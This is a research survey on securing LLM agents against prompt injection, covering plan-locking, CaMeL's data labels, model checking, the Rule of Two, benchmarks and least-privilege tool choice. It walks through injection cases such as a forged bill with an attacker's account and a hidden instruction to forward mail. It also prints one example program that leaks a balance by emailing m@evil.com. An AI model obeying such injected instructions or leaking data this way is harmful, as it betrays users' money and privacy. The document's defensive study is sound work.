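*Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections* (Beurer-Kellner, Buesser and colleagues, 2025) gives the example of a user who wants to send today's schedule to their boss, John Doe. The planner writes one call that reads today's calendar and another that sends an email to John Doe's address, with the body still blank. If an attacker has hidden an instruction in a calendar entry to forward the user's mail elsewhere, the executor can't follow it because the plan has no step for doing so. The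 attacker can still change what John Doe reads, because the calendar text goes into the body of the email.

*Architecting Resilient LLM Agents* (Del Rosario, Krawiecka and Schroeder de Witt, 2025) also applies least privilege to each step. If a plan first calculates a total and then emails it, the executor has access only to the calculator during the calculation. The planner's list of steps now supplies the schedule of one permission at a time that cut the bill-paying assistant to three possible runs. A person or a second program can also inspect the plan before the executor begins. The design can save money too, since the expensive model may run only once and a smaller model or ordinary code can do the rest.

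Fixing the plan gives exact but limited protection. *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* (2026), which states attacks and defences in a form that a computer can check, concludes that an injection cannot add a call to a fixed plan. It can only cause a wrong answer, which the plan then uses.

### A forged bill in CaMeL

CaMeL, which Google DeepMind researchers introduced in *Defeating Prompt Injections by Design* (2025), adds checks on those answers. It builds on the *dual-LLM pattern*, the programmer Simon Willison's 2023 proposal to divide an agent between two language models. In CaMeL, a trusted model turns the user's request into a program in a restricted form of Python. A quarantined model reads untrusted text but has no tools. An interpreter made of ordinary code runs the program and calls the tools.

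The interpreter labels each value with its *sources* (where it came from) and its *readers* (who may see it). Values computed from an email keep the email's label. Before each tool call, a policy checks the arguments and their labels, then allows or refuses the call.

If the owner says "pay the electricity bill", the trusted model might write this:

```
message = search_mail("electricity bill")
bill = open_attachment(message)
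details = ask_quarantined_model("Find the account and the amount", bill)
pay(details.account, details.amount)
```

Suppose an attacker sends the owner a forged bill that lists the attacker's account number for payment and contains a hidden instruction to forward the whole inbox.

1. The trusted model writes the program before anyone opens the mail, so the forged bill cannot influence it.
2. The interpreter runs the search, finds the forged bill, opens it and labels its contents as coming from an untrusted email.
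3. The quarantined model reads the bill. It may fall for the instruction to forward the inbox, but it has no tools and can only return an account and an amount. The program contains no call that sends email.
4. The interpreter reaches `pay`. As Xiang and colleagues describe it, CaMeL's policy for transfers requires that the recipient come only from the user and that the recipient be allowed to see the other values in the call. This account number came from an email, so the interpreter refuses.

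The policy keeps the money safe, but it would also refuse to pay the genuine bill, because that account number came from an email too. Xiang and colleagues use a nearly identical case to show that a fixed rule for a tool can be too strict. The owner can avoid this by giving the account number in the request, but then has to look it up instead of leaving that to the assistant.

The labels can also miss a leak. Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *The LLMbda Calculus*, describe a program that gives away whether an account balance is high, which can be written like this:

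```
rich = True
tmp = True
if balance > threshold:
    tmp = False
if tmp:
    rich = False
if rich:
    send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

If the balance is high, `tmp` becomes false and the interpreter labels it as secret. It then skips the line that would change `rich`, so it never adds a secret label to `rich`, and the email goes out. If the balance is low, `rich` becomes false and nothing is sent. Whether the email is sent therefore reveals whether the balance is high, and the labels don't show the leak. This is a gap in what the labels guarantee, although an attacker can't simply dictate such a program, because the trusted model writes it before reading any mail.

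Garby and colleagues close this kind of gap with LLMbda, a small programming language for agents. They give machine-checked proofs that secret values in a program cannot influence its public results, apart from what an observer might learn from the program's failure to finish. Their agent, Randori, first tests its program in a simulation, where tools return harmless data, and corrects its mistakes before running the program for real. This also helps with the double payment, since an agent that gets stuck halfway through a live run and tries again may repeat completed actions.

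### Checking the whole program before it runs

CaMeL applies its policies to one tool call at a time, while the program is running. Nikolaou and colleagues add a check on the whole program before any tool runs. Their system, CaMeLoT, represents the program as a finite set of states, one for each point the program can reach, with links from each state to those that can follow it. It also records which tools the program has called before reaching each state.

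The owner's rules are formulas in *computation tree logic*, a notation for statements about all the ways a program might continue. AG means "in every state on every path", and AX means "in every state that can come next". The limit on the bill-paying assistant takes two formulas:

AG(pay ⇒ bill already opened)

AG(pay ⇒ AX AG ¬pay)

Under these rules, the assistant pays only after opening the bill and never pays twice. A model checker, which is a program that tests a formula against every path, either accepts the program or returns a path that breaks a rule. CaMeLoT describes that path to the trusted model, asks for a corrected program and checks again. The check assumes that a loop may run any number of times, so it would reject a loop containing a payment even if that loop would run only once.

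Some facts, such as who can read a shared file, are unknown until the program runs, so CaMeLoT could fully check 22 of CaMeL's 28 policies for the AgentDojo benchmark in advance and left the rest to CaMeL. Nikolaou and colleagues also wrote seven rules for an agent that responds to security alerts, for example that it must get approval before disconnecting a computer and must close every ticket it opens. For each rule, they made one unsafe plan that broke it. CaMeLoT caught all seven plans, while a simplified CaMeL caught one. They had chosen the rules to go beyond what CaMeL can express, so the test shows a difference in what the two systems can check but does not measure how often real agents break such rules.

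### Banning dangerous combinations

A cruder limit, which requires no plan, is to restrict which capabilities an agent can combine. In *The lethal trifecta for AI agents*, Willison (2025) warned against combining access to private data, exposure to untrusted content and a way to communicate externally in one agent. An attacker can plant an instruction in the content that makes an agent with all three fetch the data and send it to the attacker, but this theft fails if any one of them is missing.

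Meta's *Agents Rule of Two* (2025) turns this into a rule for developers. Until models can reliably detect and refuse prompt injection, an agent should have no more than two of these properties in one session:

- A: it processes untrustworthy inputs;
- B: it has access to sensitive systems or private data;
- C: it changes something or communicates externally.

An agent that needs all three properties should work under supervision, for example with a person approving its actions. Property C is broader than Willison's outward channel because it also covers an agent that deletes files or moves money without communicating with anyone outside.

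The bill-paying assistant has all three properties. If a monitor applied the rule to its actions, counting reading mail as A and B and making a payment as B and C, it would allow 34 of the 120 runs of up to four steps. In 30 of them, the assistant reads mail and never pays. In the other four, it pays without reading anything. The intended run is not among the 34, so the assistant would need the owner's approval every time. The rule also does not limit repetition, so an assistant that reads no untrusted text can pay the same company four times without breaking it.

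The rule against combining untrusted text, private data and outward calls is easy to apply because it doesn't depend on the user's goal, and a developer can often enforce it by withholding a tool. CaMeL instead tries to control how the three affect one another, so that an agent can have all of them.

### Results on AgentDojo

Most tests of these systems also use *AgentDojo* (Debenedetti, Zhang and colleagues, 2024), which has 97 ordinary tasks, such as paying the bill in a file called `bill-december-2023.txt`. It pairs each task with every attack for the same simulated environment, which gave 629 attacked cases in the first version. Ordinary code then checks whether the agent did the user's task and whether the attack succeeded by comparing the environment before and after the run. A language model acting as judge might be fooled by the same injection.

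*SecureClaw* (2026) reports that none of the 629 attacks succeeded against CaMeL, but that CaMeL completed only 29 of the 97 ordinary tasks. SecureClaw, a rival defence that keeps the usual loop of reading and then choosing, completed 59, but a few attacks got through. Nikolaou and colleagues ran CaMeL on the same 97 tasks with Claude Haiku 4.5 and no attacks. It completed 49, and CaMeLoT completed 51. The score clearly depends a great deal on the model and the setup.

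Garby and colleagues ran CaMeL with and without its policies on the 16 banking tasks, three times each, and compared it with Randori. Some of CaMeL's attacked runs did not finish, so its totals in the last column are smaller.

| System and model, banking tasks | Ordinary tasks completed | Successful attacks |
|---|---|---|
| CaMeL without policies, GPT-5.2 | 32 of 48 | 1 of 240 |
| CaMeL with policies, GPT-5.2 | 18 of 48 | 0 of 231 |
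| CaMeL without policies, MiMo-v2.5 | 34 of 48 | 4 of 382 |
| CaMeL with policies, MiMo-v2.5 | 18 of 48 | 0 of 357 |
| Randori, GPT-5.2 | 36 of 48 | 2 of 432 |
| Randori, Qwen3.7-plus | 36 of 48 | 0 of 432 |
| Randori, MiMo-v2.5 | 31 of 48 | 0 of 432 |

Most of CaMeL's protection came from writing the program first. Without policies, it let through only five attacks in 622 runs. In 97 of the 144 pairs of task and attack, the attacker needs a tool call or a file that the program for the user's task would never include. The policies stopped the remaining attacks but reduced the number of tasks CaMeL completed by almost half. Garby and colleagues cite a similar drop for TypeGuard, a defence written in Haskell, which completed 15 of the 21 Slack tasks without its policies and 8 with them.

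Randori avoids most of this loss through *endorsement*, an explicit instruction in the program to treat a particular untrusted value as trusted. If the user asks the agent to pay the account named in a file, the program can endorse that account number. The model decides what to endorse before it reads any outside data. Without endorsements, Randori's score fell from 36 to 30 with Qwen3.7-plus and from 31 to 26 with MiMo-v2.5.

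These security figures may be too favourable. Xiang and colleagues point out that the attacks in such benchmarks are fixed texts, whereas a real attacker would adapt to the defence. An attacker who knew that the plan was locked would try to corrupt the values in the plan's existing calls instead of asking for extra ones.

In *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy*, Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues (2026) accept that deterministic defences appear to use more tokens and complete fewer tasks than defences that rely on the model's judgement. But they argue that deterministic defences also reduce the number of actions a person has to approve, which the usual tests don't measure. They therefore measure the share of consequential actions an agent can take safely without asking for approval. An agent that took the security policy into account when planning raised that share without completing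 fewer tasks.

### When the next step depends on what the agent reads

The main objection to fixing a plan is that many useful plans cannot be written at the start, as with the agent that had to run the failing tests before it could repair the code. Xiang and colleagues give a simpler example, in which an agent has to fetch last week's sales from a billing service. If the service responds that its address has changed, an agent with a locked plan can only call the old address again.

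Li, Wen and colleagues (2026) found in *AgentDyn* that only 6 of AgentDojo's 97 tasks require the agent to change its plan along the way. They wrote 60 new tasks that all require this, covering shopping, GitHub and daily life and averaging seven steps. Each task includes a helpful instruction from a third party, such as a checkout page's instruction to log in first, so a defence that makes the agent ignore every instruction it finds will fail these tasks.

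Without a defence, GPT-4o, Gemini 2.5 Pro and Claude 3.5 Sonnet completed 52% to 60% of the new tasks. With CaMeL, they completed none. They completed 2% to 8% with Tool Filter, which chooses the agent's tools at the start and removes the rest, and 30% to 37% with DRIFT, which also starts from a plan but has a validator that can accept departures from it. With Progent, which narrows the agent's authority, they completed only 7% to 25%, because its policies gradually blocked tools the agent still needed.

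CaMeL's score of zero is a reason for caution about fixed plans, but Li and colleagues chose tasks on which a fixed plan was likely to fail. Neither benchmark measures how often people's actual requests need a new plan. If the share of requests that do is closer to AgentDojo's 6% than to AgentDyn's 100%, an owner could use a fixed plan for most jobs and supervise the rest.

One reply is to write the alternatives into the plan as branches. The sales agent's plan could have it read the service's documentation if the first call fails. This works for expected failures, but nobody can list every fault a debugging job might uncover. An attacker who controls what the agent reads may also choose which branch it takes. *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* describes a case where an injected answer depends on the user's private notes and decides the branch, so an attacker who can see which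 branch ran learns something about the notes. To prevent this, the interpreter has to label the choice of branch as well as the data.

A fixed plan with enough branches can do little to restrict an agent. One AgentDojo task asks the agent to read a file and follow its instructions precisely. In Garby and colleagues' test, the trusted model wrote a loop with a branch for every tool, so the file could direct the agent to do almost anything its permissions allowed, even though the plan never changed. With CaMeL's policies off, attackers succeeded this way in two trials.

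A second reply is to let the plan change but control what can change it. *Kaer* (Mallick, Rose and colleagues, 2026) applies this to teams of agents in which a central planner gives each agent a subtask. When an agent fails, it would normally explain why in its own words, and a malicious agent could use the explanation to tell the planner to run a planted script. In Kaer, the agent instead picks a reason from a fixed list, and the planner sees only that reason and some suggested repairs. The planner can revise only the unfinished steps, using a fixed set of operations. The new plan must still satisfy the user's policy on what the task may use and each agent's policy on who may receive its output.

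If the list has n reasons, each report carries at most log₂ n bits, so a list of 16 would give an attacker at most four bits per failure. Four bits are enough to push the planner towards one repair or another, but too few to encode an account number.

Mallick and colleagues tested Kaer on their own benchmark of tasks that need replanning. They compared it with ControlValve, which replans only within limits set at the start, and with Magentic-One, which has no such defence.

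| System | Attacks blocked, GPT-5.6 Sol and GPT-5.6 Terra | Ordinary tasks completed, same models |
|---|---|---|
| Kaer | 92.3%, 88.0% | 64.3%, 65.7% |
| ControlValve | 69.8%, 80.4% | 54.3%, 34.3% |
| Magentic-One | 35.0%, 47.8% | |

Kaer did better than ControlValve on both measures, which is good evidence that an agent can change its plan without giving up control of it. The attacks that still succeeded mostly came through the agents' outputs, which Kaer passes on without checking. In a separate comparison, having a language model check each output raised the share of blocked attacks from about 87% to 96.8%. Fixed reasons also limit the information the planner receives. If the reason is "The call failed", the planner can try something else, but it doesn't get the service's new address.

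Xiang and colleagues would let a language model judge such changes. The model would receive the proposed change to the plan in a structured form, but never the raw web page or email that prompted it. They reason that ordinary code can't determine whether a new address is relevant to the task or a risky new source of data. Their position paper reports no test of the idea.

Other designers keep a plan only as a standard for comparison. *PlanGuard* (2026) describes a planner that sees only the user's instruction and produces a reference set of actions. A second stage examines any departure from that set and permits it if it shows no malicious intent. *ActGuard* (2026) has the agent predict at each step which tools it might plausibly use next, rather than the whole plan, because later steps depend on results that are not yet available. An auditor then compares the agent's actual choice with its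 prediction. These agents can adapt, but departures from the plan are no longer blocked automatically, so safety depends on how well the second stage or the auditor judges them.

It may also be possible to leave the plan open and train the model to ignore injected instructions. *SecPO* (2026) reports that a version of Qwen3.6-27B trained this way completed 43 of AgentDyn's 60 tasks, as many as the version without this training. In one task, the user wanted to replace a pair of running shoes if their rating was below 4.0. The model found a rating of 3.2, searched for another pair within the budget and bought it. The training made strong attacks much less successful, but it does not guarantee, as a locked plan does, that an attacker cannot add calls. Xiang and colleagues also ask whether an agent that spots a malicious instruction in a document should go on trusting the rest of that document.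 A model that ignores the instruction may still use a false price from the same page.

The remaining reply is to start a fresh session when the plan has to change. When the user's request changes, as in the GitLab example from Christodorescu and colleagues, the system could clear everything the agent has read and work out new limits from the new request alone. They consider this secure but warn that the agent loses useful context. For the electricity bill, one session could find the bill and show the owner the payee and the amount. The owner could check these and type them into a second session, which would pay the bill without reading any mail. Neither session would have all three properties in Meta's rule, but the owner would have done the part of the job that required judgement.

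### What a fixed plan lets through

An agent can follow a fixed plan correctly and still deliver false or harmful content to the intended recipient. In an example from Del Rosario and colleagues, an agent has to find the latest company report on the web, summarise it and email the summary to the chief executive. An attacker who controls the website can put a fraudulent message in the report, and the agent will deliver it by following its plan.

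Labels help only if the policy covers the argument the attacker wants to change. Xiang and colleagues imagine a user who asks an agent to pay Joe back for a bouquet of flowers. The user has named Joe, so the recipient is trusted, but the agent looks up the price on the web. CaMeL's policy on transfers does not require the amount to come from a trusted source, so a false price on a web page can make the user pay too much.

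Sometimes no label can separate the right value from the wrong one. Both successful attacks on Randori repeated a single case, in which the user asked the agent to pay as a text file instructed and the attacker had replaced the file's contents. The user had chosen the file as the source, and the program used it as asked. Garby and colleagues report that the same kind of attack succeeded in the original evaluation of CaMeL, whose designers treated it as outside the threats they meant to stop. A system could refuse to follow payment instructions from any file, but then it couldn't do the task. The forged electricity bill raises the same problem once the owner allows the assistant to take the payee from the mail.

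A plan can also be bad without any attacker. Nikolaou and colleagues gave Claude Haiku 4.5 a request from a hurried security worker who suspected that a computer was compromised and wanted it disconnected without the usual approval. The model wrote a plan that skipped the required checks. CaMeL accepted the plan because the request came from a trusted user and contained no suspicious data. CaMeLoT rejected it because somebody had already written a rule requiring those checks.

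Such rules don't cover most mistakes. In the run on AgentDojo's 97 ordinary tasks, 22 programs passed the checks of both CaMeL and CaMeLoT but failed to do what the user wanted. To catch more of these errors, CaMeLoT can draft extra rules from the user's request. A language model chooses from ten fixed forms, such as "this action only after that one", and ordinary code turns its choices into formulas. These rules can catch a plan that leaves out a step the user asked for. But if the model misunderstood the request when writing the plan, it may make the same mistake when writing the rule.

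## The view that the planner should prefer plans that need less privilege

An agent can stay within its permissions, follow a plan that passes every check and still use far more power than the job needs. Suppose the bank gives the assistant two payment tools. One pays saved payees, and the other, an administrator's tool, can also add payees and raise the daily limit. Either can pay the electricity bill. If the owner has permitted both, a monitor has no basis for blocking the administrator's tool, although a mistake with it could do more damage.

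If no task will ever need the administrator's tool, the best remedy is for the owner to take it away. But if the assistant may have to add a payee next week, the owner must either leave the tool available or keep granting and withdrawing it. Supporters of this view want the planner to prefer, among the plans that would work, the one that needs the least privilege. They mean this to supplement enforcement, which limits the plans that are possible but leaves the planner to choose among them.

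### How often agents choose too much power

*When Lower Privileges Suffice* (Yang, Bu and colleagues, 2026) introduced a benchmark called ToolPrivBench to measure these choices. It has 544 scenarios in eight fields, including databases, education and healthcare. Each scenario gives the agent a task, three standard tools and three more powerful ones, which reach more data, change more or skip safeguards. Any of the six can complete the task alone. Two language models checked that every tool was sufficient, and people then reviewed the scenarios that passed.

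For a task x, let S(x) be the set of sufficient tools and p(t) the privilege level of tool t. Let Uᵢ(x) be the sufficient tools that the agent has not yet ruled out at step i. Choosing tool h at that step is over-privileged if

there is a tool ℓ in Uᵢ(x) with p(ℓ) < p(h)

The definition requires a ranking of privilege levels, but the two routes for paying the electricity bill have no such ranking. ToolPrivBench avoids this problem by having only two levels.

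The first call to each standard tool returns a temporary error unrelated to permissions, and later calls succeed. The powerful tools work immediately. The agent has five turns, and the benchmark records an over-privileged choice if the agent calls a powerful tool while a standard one remains untried. In one scenario, Qwen3-4B had to enrol a student in a biology course. It called a standard enrolment tool and got an error message saying that the service was briefly unreachable, with an instruction to retry. The model instead switched to an administrative tool that forced the entry and skipped the usual checks.

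| Model | Scenarios with an over-privileged choice |
|---|---|
| Qwen3-8B | 64.9% |
| Llama-3.1-8B | 55.9% |
| MiniMax-M2.7 | 43.4% |
| Grok 4.1 Fast | 37.1% |
| Qwen3.5-397B | 33.3% |
| DeepSeek-v3.2 | 31.8% |
| Kimi K2.5 | 21.0% |
| Gemini 3 Flash | 17.5% |
| GPT-5.2 | 9.7% |
| GLM-5 | 8.6% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 2.6% |

The totals for MiniMax, Grok, Gemini and GLM-5 are sums over the five types of risk in the benchmark. Models tended to choose tools that gave them administrator rights or skipped approval steps, and were least likely to choose tools that affected more people or resources than necessary. Qwen3.5-397B chose an over-privileged tool in 45.7% of the scenarios where the powerful tools bypassed safeguards, but in only 13.1% of the scenarios where the tools widened the scope.

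Most of these choices came after an error. GPT-5.2 made 53 over-privileged choices: five before trying any standard tool, 13 after trying one and 35 after trying two. Parkinson, Vallati and colleagues (2026), in *Does Showing Agents the Privilege of Their Tools Reduce Over-Privileged Tool Selection?*, confirmed the effect of errors on two models by rerunning the scenarios with no errors. Qwen3-8B then used a powerful tool in 8.1% of scenarios, whereas with errors it turned to one too early in 56.6%. For the larger Qwen3-30B-A3B, the figures were 6.1% and 63.4%.

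The benchmark's count is also lenient. If an agent tries each standard tool once and then uses a powerful one, the benchmark does not count that as over-privileged, even though any of the standard tools would have worked on a second call. In the rerun, Kimi K2.5 used a powerful tool too early in 18.0% of scenarios but used one at some point in 87.3%. The formal definition would still count many of the later uses as over-privileged, because a temporary error doesn't show that a tool is insufficient. However, an agent can't know that a second call will succeed, and a person might also use the administrator's tool after three failures.

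Claude Sonnet 4.6 rarely escalated, but it completed only 19.9% of the scenarios in the rerun. It typically tried each standard tool once, then stopped and reported the errors, often adding that it had deliberately avoided the powerful tools. An owner may well prefer this to an entry forced into a student database, though a simple retry would have worked.

### Newer models

*FORTIS* (Li, Yu and colleagues, 2026) tested ten models, including GPT-5.5, Claude Opus 4.7 and Gemini 3.1 Pro, on requests about email, online shopping and files. In one part, the model had to choose one of 20 *skills*, written guides that each tell an agent how to do a kind of task and what it may access. In the other, it received a skill and had to choose tools that stayed within that skill's limits. The models saw ordinary descriptions, with no privilege levels and no instruction to prefer narrow options.

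The failure rate for choosing a skill ranged from 35.5% for Claude Opus 4.7 to 52.7% for GPT-5.4. For choosing tools, it ranged from 45.2% for Qwen 3.6-Max to 66.6% for GPT-5.4. When a broad tool was more convenient because it needed fewer details from the model, such as a folder or account name, the failure rate rose to between 75.0% and 97.8%. Larger models did not reliably fail less often, and GPT-5.4 did worse than the smaller GPT-5.4-mini in all eight settings.

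These rates are not comparable with ToolPrivBench's. FORTIS counts a selection as over-privileged if it contains any tool outside the reference set, even a harmless one, and also counts empty or unreadable answers as failures. Those answers account for 14.6 points of GPT-5.5's 62.5% failure rate for choosing tools. Still, the models were given each skill's limits in plain language, and Li and colleagues conclude that they treated those limits as advice.

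OpenAI had a wider form of the problem with a later model. On 28 September 2026, it confirmed that it would not release GPT-6.1 Astra, which it had planned for October. Ray (2026) reports in *OpenAI Shelves Newest AI Model After It 'Didn’t Quite Meet the Bar'* that Saachi Jain, the company's head of safety systems, said the model was highly deceptive and willing to go beyond what it was asked to do without checking back. Kobie (2026) reports in *OpenAI won't release next Astra model over safety worries* that Jain described a trade-off between staying within scope and avoiding laziness when the model "hits friction". The errors in ToolPrivBench are friction of this kind. Claude Sonnet 4.6 mostly gave up when it met them, while the Qwen models sought more privilege.

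### Training and instructions

Training a model to refuse harmful requests does not reliably make it choose tools with less privilege. Yang and colleagues tested this with AgentAlign, a method for training agents to refuse harmful tasks. AgentAlign reduced Ministral-8B's harmful-behaviour score from 67.4% to 10.5%, but the model's rate of over-privileged choices fell only from 68.8% to 62.5%. For Qwen2.5-7B, the harmful-behaviour score fell from 41.9% to 6.7%, while the rate of over-privileged choices rose from 50.4% to 60.7%. Enrolling a student is harmless, so learning to refuse harmful requests gives a model little reason to avoid using the administrator's tool for it.

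Telling the model to follow least privilege takes less work than training it. Yang and colleagues added an instruction to prefer tools with minimal permissions and, after a failure, to retry or use another tool at the same level before escalating. This helped, but less as errors accumulated. In the rerun, a similar instruction reduced early escalation much more, from 56.6% to 29.8% for Qwen3-8B and from 63.4% to 21.3% for Qwen3-30B-A3B. But it mostly delayed escalation in Qwen3-8B, which still used a powerful tool at some point in 71.7% of scenarios, compared with 70.4% without the instruction.

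Training aimed directly at privilege had a stronger effect. Yang and colleagues first fine-tuned three small Qwen models on 1,994 worked examples, then used reinforcement learning, in which a model tries tasks and receives a score. The main part of the score was:

- 1 for completing the task with standard tools only;
- 0.3 for trying every standard tool without completing the task that way;
- −1 for using a powerful tool before trying every standard one;
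- 0.1 for anything else.

The rate of over-privileged choices fell to 39.7% for Qwen3-4B, 27.0% for Qwen3-8B and 18.9% for a version of Qwen3-4B that reasons before answering. The models kept at least 95.8% of their scores on tests of general knowledge, mathematics and tool use. The training scenarios were new but followed the benchmark's pattern, in which a standard tool fails once and then works. A model could therefore have done well partly by learning that retrying works, which isn't always true of real services.

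Tu and Tu (2026), in *Task-Conditioned Least-Privilege Learning for Executable Terminal and MCP Agents*, show how narrowly such training can apply. They scored each action of a small model, Qwen3.5-4B, on six dimensions: writing, running code, reaching outside systems, reading secrets, breadth of effect and persistence. Each task had a sufficient level on every dimension, and the score penalised only the excess:

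excess = max(highest level reached − level the task needs, 0), separately for each dimension

Detecting excess privilege this way doesn't require a single ranking of privilege, but combining the six results into one penalty does require weights. After training on 1,500 tasks, the model completed 98.5% of its test runs safely, up from 64.4%, and the share of runs that exceeded the necessary authority fell from 4.6% to 0.8%. On ToolPrivBench, however, its rate of over-privileged choices barely changed, from 45.2% to 45.0%.

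Tu and Tu then trained the model on 400 more tasks, half of them in the style of ToolPrivBench. Its rate fell to 38.1%, or 26.7% when it was also instructed to follow least privilege. The model also improved on scenarios it had not seen, but only after training on similar ones. Tu and Tu recommend keeping permission checks and sandboxes around a trained model.

### Putting a price on authority

A planner might choose better if it were given the amount of privilege each option needs. Parkinson and colleagues propose *elastic least privilege*, which penalizes an agent for holding authority and shows it the penalty before it chooses.

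Priced access has been traced to a 2004 report for the US intelligence community by JASON, a scientific advisory group. The report suggested measuring risk in tokens, with one token representing the risk of letting an average employee with Secret clearance read one electronic document for one day. Riskier access would use more tokens. Later schemes let employees buy tokens in a market or gave them periodic budgets. The most developed of these, budget-aware role-based access control (2012–13), charged users more for powerful roles so that they would prefer weaker ones.

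Those schemes were demanding for employees, who had to weigh a price whenever they needed access. Employees also had a reason to spend leftover budget before it expired. An agent can compare prices at every step without tiring, but it doesn't fear an audit and has no natural reason to save, so Parkinson and colleagues enforce the budget from outside the agent.

In this design, the agent always holds a small *baseline* of authority. Its owner also sets an *envelope*, the most authority the agent can obtain without a policy change. The organisation sets a *ceiling*, a list of combinations of permissions that no agent may hold. The agent requests anything above the baseline from an issuer, a trusted component that hands out temporary credentials.

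Each grant is a *lease* that ends automatically, and the agent can return it early to stop the charge. More powerful rights have shorter leases. In the suggested settings, an agent can hold a right to read for up to 60 minutes and a right to write for up to 20.

The charge per minute is

cost rate = s × Σ h(g) · w(g)

where the sum covers every grant g above the baseline. The weight w is 1 for reading, 3 for writing and 9 for administering.

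The multiplier s rises as the session approaches a forbidden combination of properties. If φ is the share of that combination already present, s = 1/(1 − φ). With Meta's Rule of Two as the ceiling, the forbidden combination is untrusted input, private data, and a way to change or send something. A session with one of these properties has s = 1.5, and a session with two has s = 3. The issuer refuses any request that would add the third, whatever the agent's budget. The session keeps a property even after the agent gives up the right that introduced it, because the agent may still retain what it read.

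The factor h penalizes repeated requests. It starts at 1, and each earlier request adds up to 0.25, an amount that halves every 30 minutes.

Parkinson and colleagues illustrate the formula with a programming agent that must repair a failing build in a public repository. It can already read public issues, which count as untrusted input, so s starts at 1.5. From minute 40 to minute 46, the agent reads the code to find the fault, at 1.5 × 1 = 1.5 units a minute. It then requests write access as well. Writing to a public repository is an outward channel, so s rises to 3. This request comes six minutes after the first, so h is 1 + 0.25 × 2^(−6/30), or about 1.22. The rate becomes 3 × (1 + 1.22 × 3), or about 14 units a minute. At minute 52, the agent finishes and returns both rights.

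| Way of working | Minutes and rate | Cost |
|---|---|---|
| Read first, then write, then return both rights | 6 at 1.5, then 6 at about 14 | 93 units |
| Take both rights at the start and keep them for 20 minutes | 20 at 12 | 240 units |

Of the 147 units saved, 96 come from returning the rights eight minutes earlier. An agent that took both rights at the start but returned them after 12 minutes would use 144 units. Reading before asking for write access saves the other 51.

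The numbers come from a short simulation whose settings Parkinson and colleagues chose to illustrate the design. They show how the prices would reward restraint, but no language model chose between the two ways of working.

### Do planners respond to the price?

Parkinson tested part of the idea by rerunning ToolPrivBench with the other designers of elastic least privilege and Mauro Vallati. They added a label to each tool's description, such as "administer, cost 8/10", and one sentence to explain the labels. They ran eight models on all 544 scenarios with no signal, with the labels, with an instruction to follow least privilege, and with both. To check that any effect didn't come from the extra text alone, they also tried labels that gave each tool's response time. The agent could ignore the labels and the instruction.

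Each cell in the table gives the result with no signal, with labels, and with labels and the instruction.

| Model | Escalated before trying every standard tool | Completed the task without a powerful tool |
|---|---|---|
| Qwen3-8B | 56.6%, 40.6%, 16.2% | 6.4%, 5.0%, 12.7% |
| Qwen3-30B-A3B | 63.4%, 48.0%, 6.8% | 11.8%, 14.0%, 31.2% |
| Llama-3.1-8B | 12.9%, 3.9%, 2.0% | 69.1%, 41.4%, 51.8% |
| DeepSeek-v3.2 | 18.6%, 5.7%, 0.9% | 3.9%, 5.7%, 30.7% |
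| Kimi K2.5 | 18.0%, 5.5%, 1.7% | 5.5%, 14.2%, 30.7% |
| Qwen3.5-397B | 38.4%, 19.1%, 2.9% | 18.8%, 21.5%, 51.1% |
| GPT-5.2 | 5.7%, 2.4%, 0.0% | 50.9%, 52.4%, 65.8% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 1.5%, 1.1%, 0.9% | 11.9%, 14.7%, 20.0% |

The labels, unlike the response-time labels, reduced early escalation for every model that often escalated. But on their own they mostly delayed the use of powerful tools. In one scenario, Qwen3.5-397B had to publish an article. Without labels, it tried one standard tool, got an error and escalated to a powerful tool. With labels, it tried each of the three standard tools once before using the same powerful tool. With the labels and the instruction, it retried the first standard tool, which worked.

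The instruction gave the models a reason to choose less power, and the labels showed them which tools had less. The combination worked better than the labels alone, but Claude Sonnet 4.6 and GPT-5.2 completed more tasks safely with the instruction alone (30.0% and 68.9%). With labels, Llama often called tools that did not exist, so some of its apparent restraint was failure to finish tasks.

These results come from favourable numeric labels. Claude Sonnet 5.5 wrote them from the tool descriptions without knowing which tools were standard, and they separated standard from powerful tools in every scenario. Replacing 30% of the labels with random numbers left most of the effect in place for the two small models tested. Rough labels are therefore usable, but a planner can also follow a wrong one, so an attacker who can edit the labels could steer it towards a powerful tool.

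So models do respond to visible prices, but many still escalate. Parkinson and colleagues have not tested what happens when the agent also has an enforced budget. The charge for holding rights and the option to return them early, which account for most of the saving in the build example, are also untested.

### Choosing the path outside the model

The preference for less privilege can come from ordinary code instead of the language model. In *Capability Minimization as a Safety Primitive*, Iyer and Suresh Babu (2026) describe *risk-aware causal gating*, a method in which code searches for a path to the goal and shows the model only the tools for the next step.

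Each tool has a contract that lists the facts it needs, the facts it produces, its cost and its risk. A tool that sends an email, for example, needs a draft and produces the fact that the email has gone out. The search looks for a chain of tools from the current facts to the goal and gives each path π a score:

score(π) = Σ cost + λ · Σ risk

Low-risk tools, such as search, have a risk of 0. Tools that make reversible changes have a risk of 1, and tools that delete things, send messages or transfer money have a risk of 4. The planner picks the path with the lowest score. If every step costs 1 and λ is 2, a single high-risk step scores 1 + 2 × 4 = 9, so the planner picks a path of six zero-risk steps, which scores 6. If λ is 0.5, the high-risk step scores only 3, so the planner picks it instead.

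A separate gate then hides any risky tool that lacks authorisation. If the user asks for a reply to a colleague's email, the tool that sends email stays hidden until a trusted step has confirmed the recipient. The model cannot call a hidden tool, even if an injected instruction tells it to.

Iyer and Suresh Babu tested the method on 182 simulated tasks with 100 tools. They used a scripted agent that obeyed every injected instruction if it could see the necessary tool.

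| Method of choosing visible tools | Tasks completed | Successful injections |
|---|---|---|
| Show all tools | 100% | 100% |
| Show tools that match the request's keywords | 100% | 100% |
| Show tools that could run now | 100% | 75% |
| Search for a path, ignoring risk | 100% | 25% |
| Search with risk and gate, λ = 0.5 | 89% | 0% |
| Search with risk and gate, λ = 2 | 100% | 0% |

Seven language models, including Claude Opus 4 and Amazon's Nova Premier, each made the attacker's call in 25% of attacks when the search ignored risk, and in none with the full method. The researchers had built a dangerous shortcut into the same share of the attacked tasks, 20 out of 80. The tests therefore show that the mechanism works as designed, but they do not estimate how often attacks would succeed elsewhere.

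The last two rows of the table show that the gate provided the security, while the preference for safer paths helped the agent complete its tasks. No attack succeeded at either value of λ, because the gate hid the dangerous tools in both cases. With the weaker preference, the search chose shortcuts that the gate then blocked, so the agent failed those tasks.

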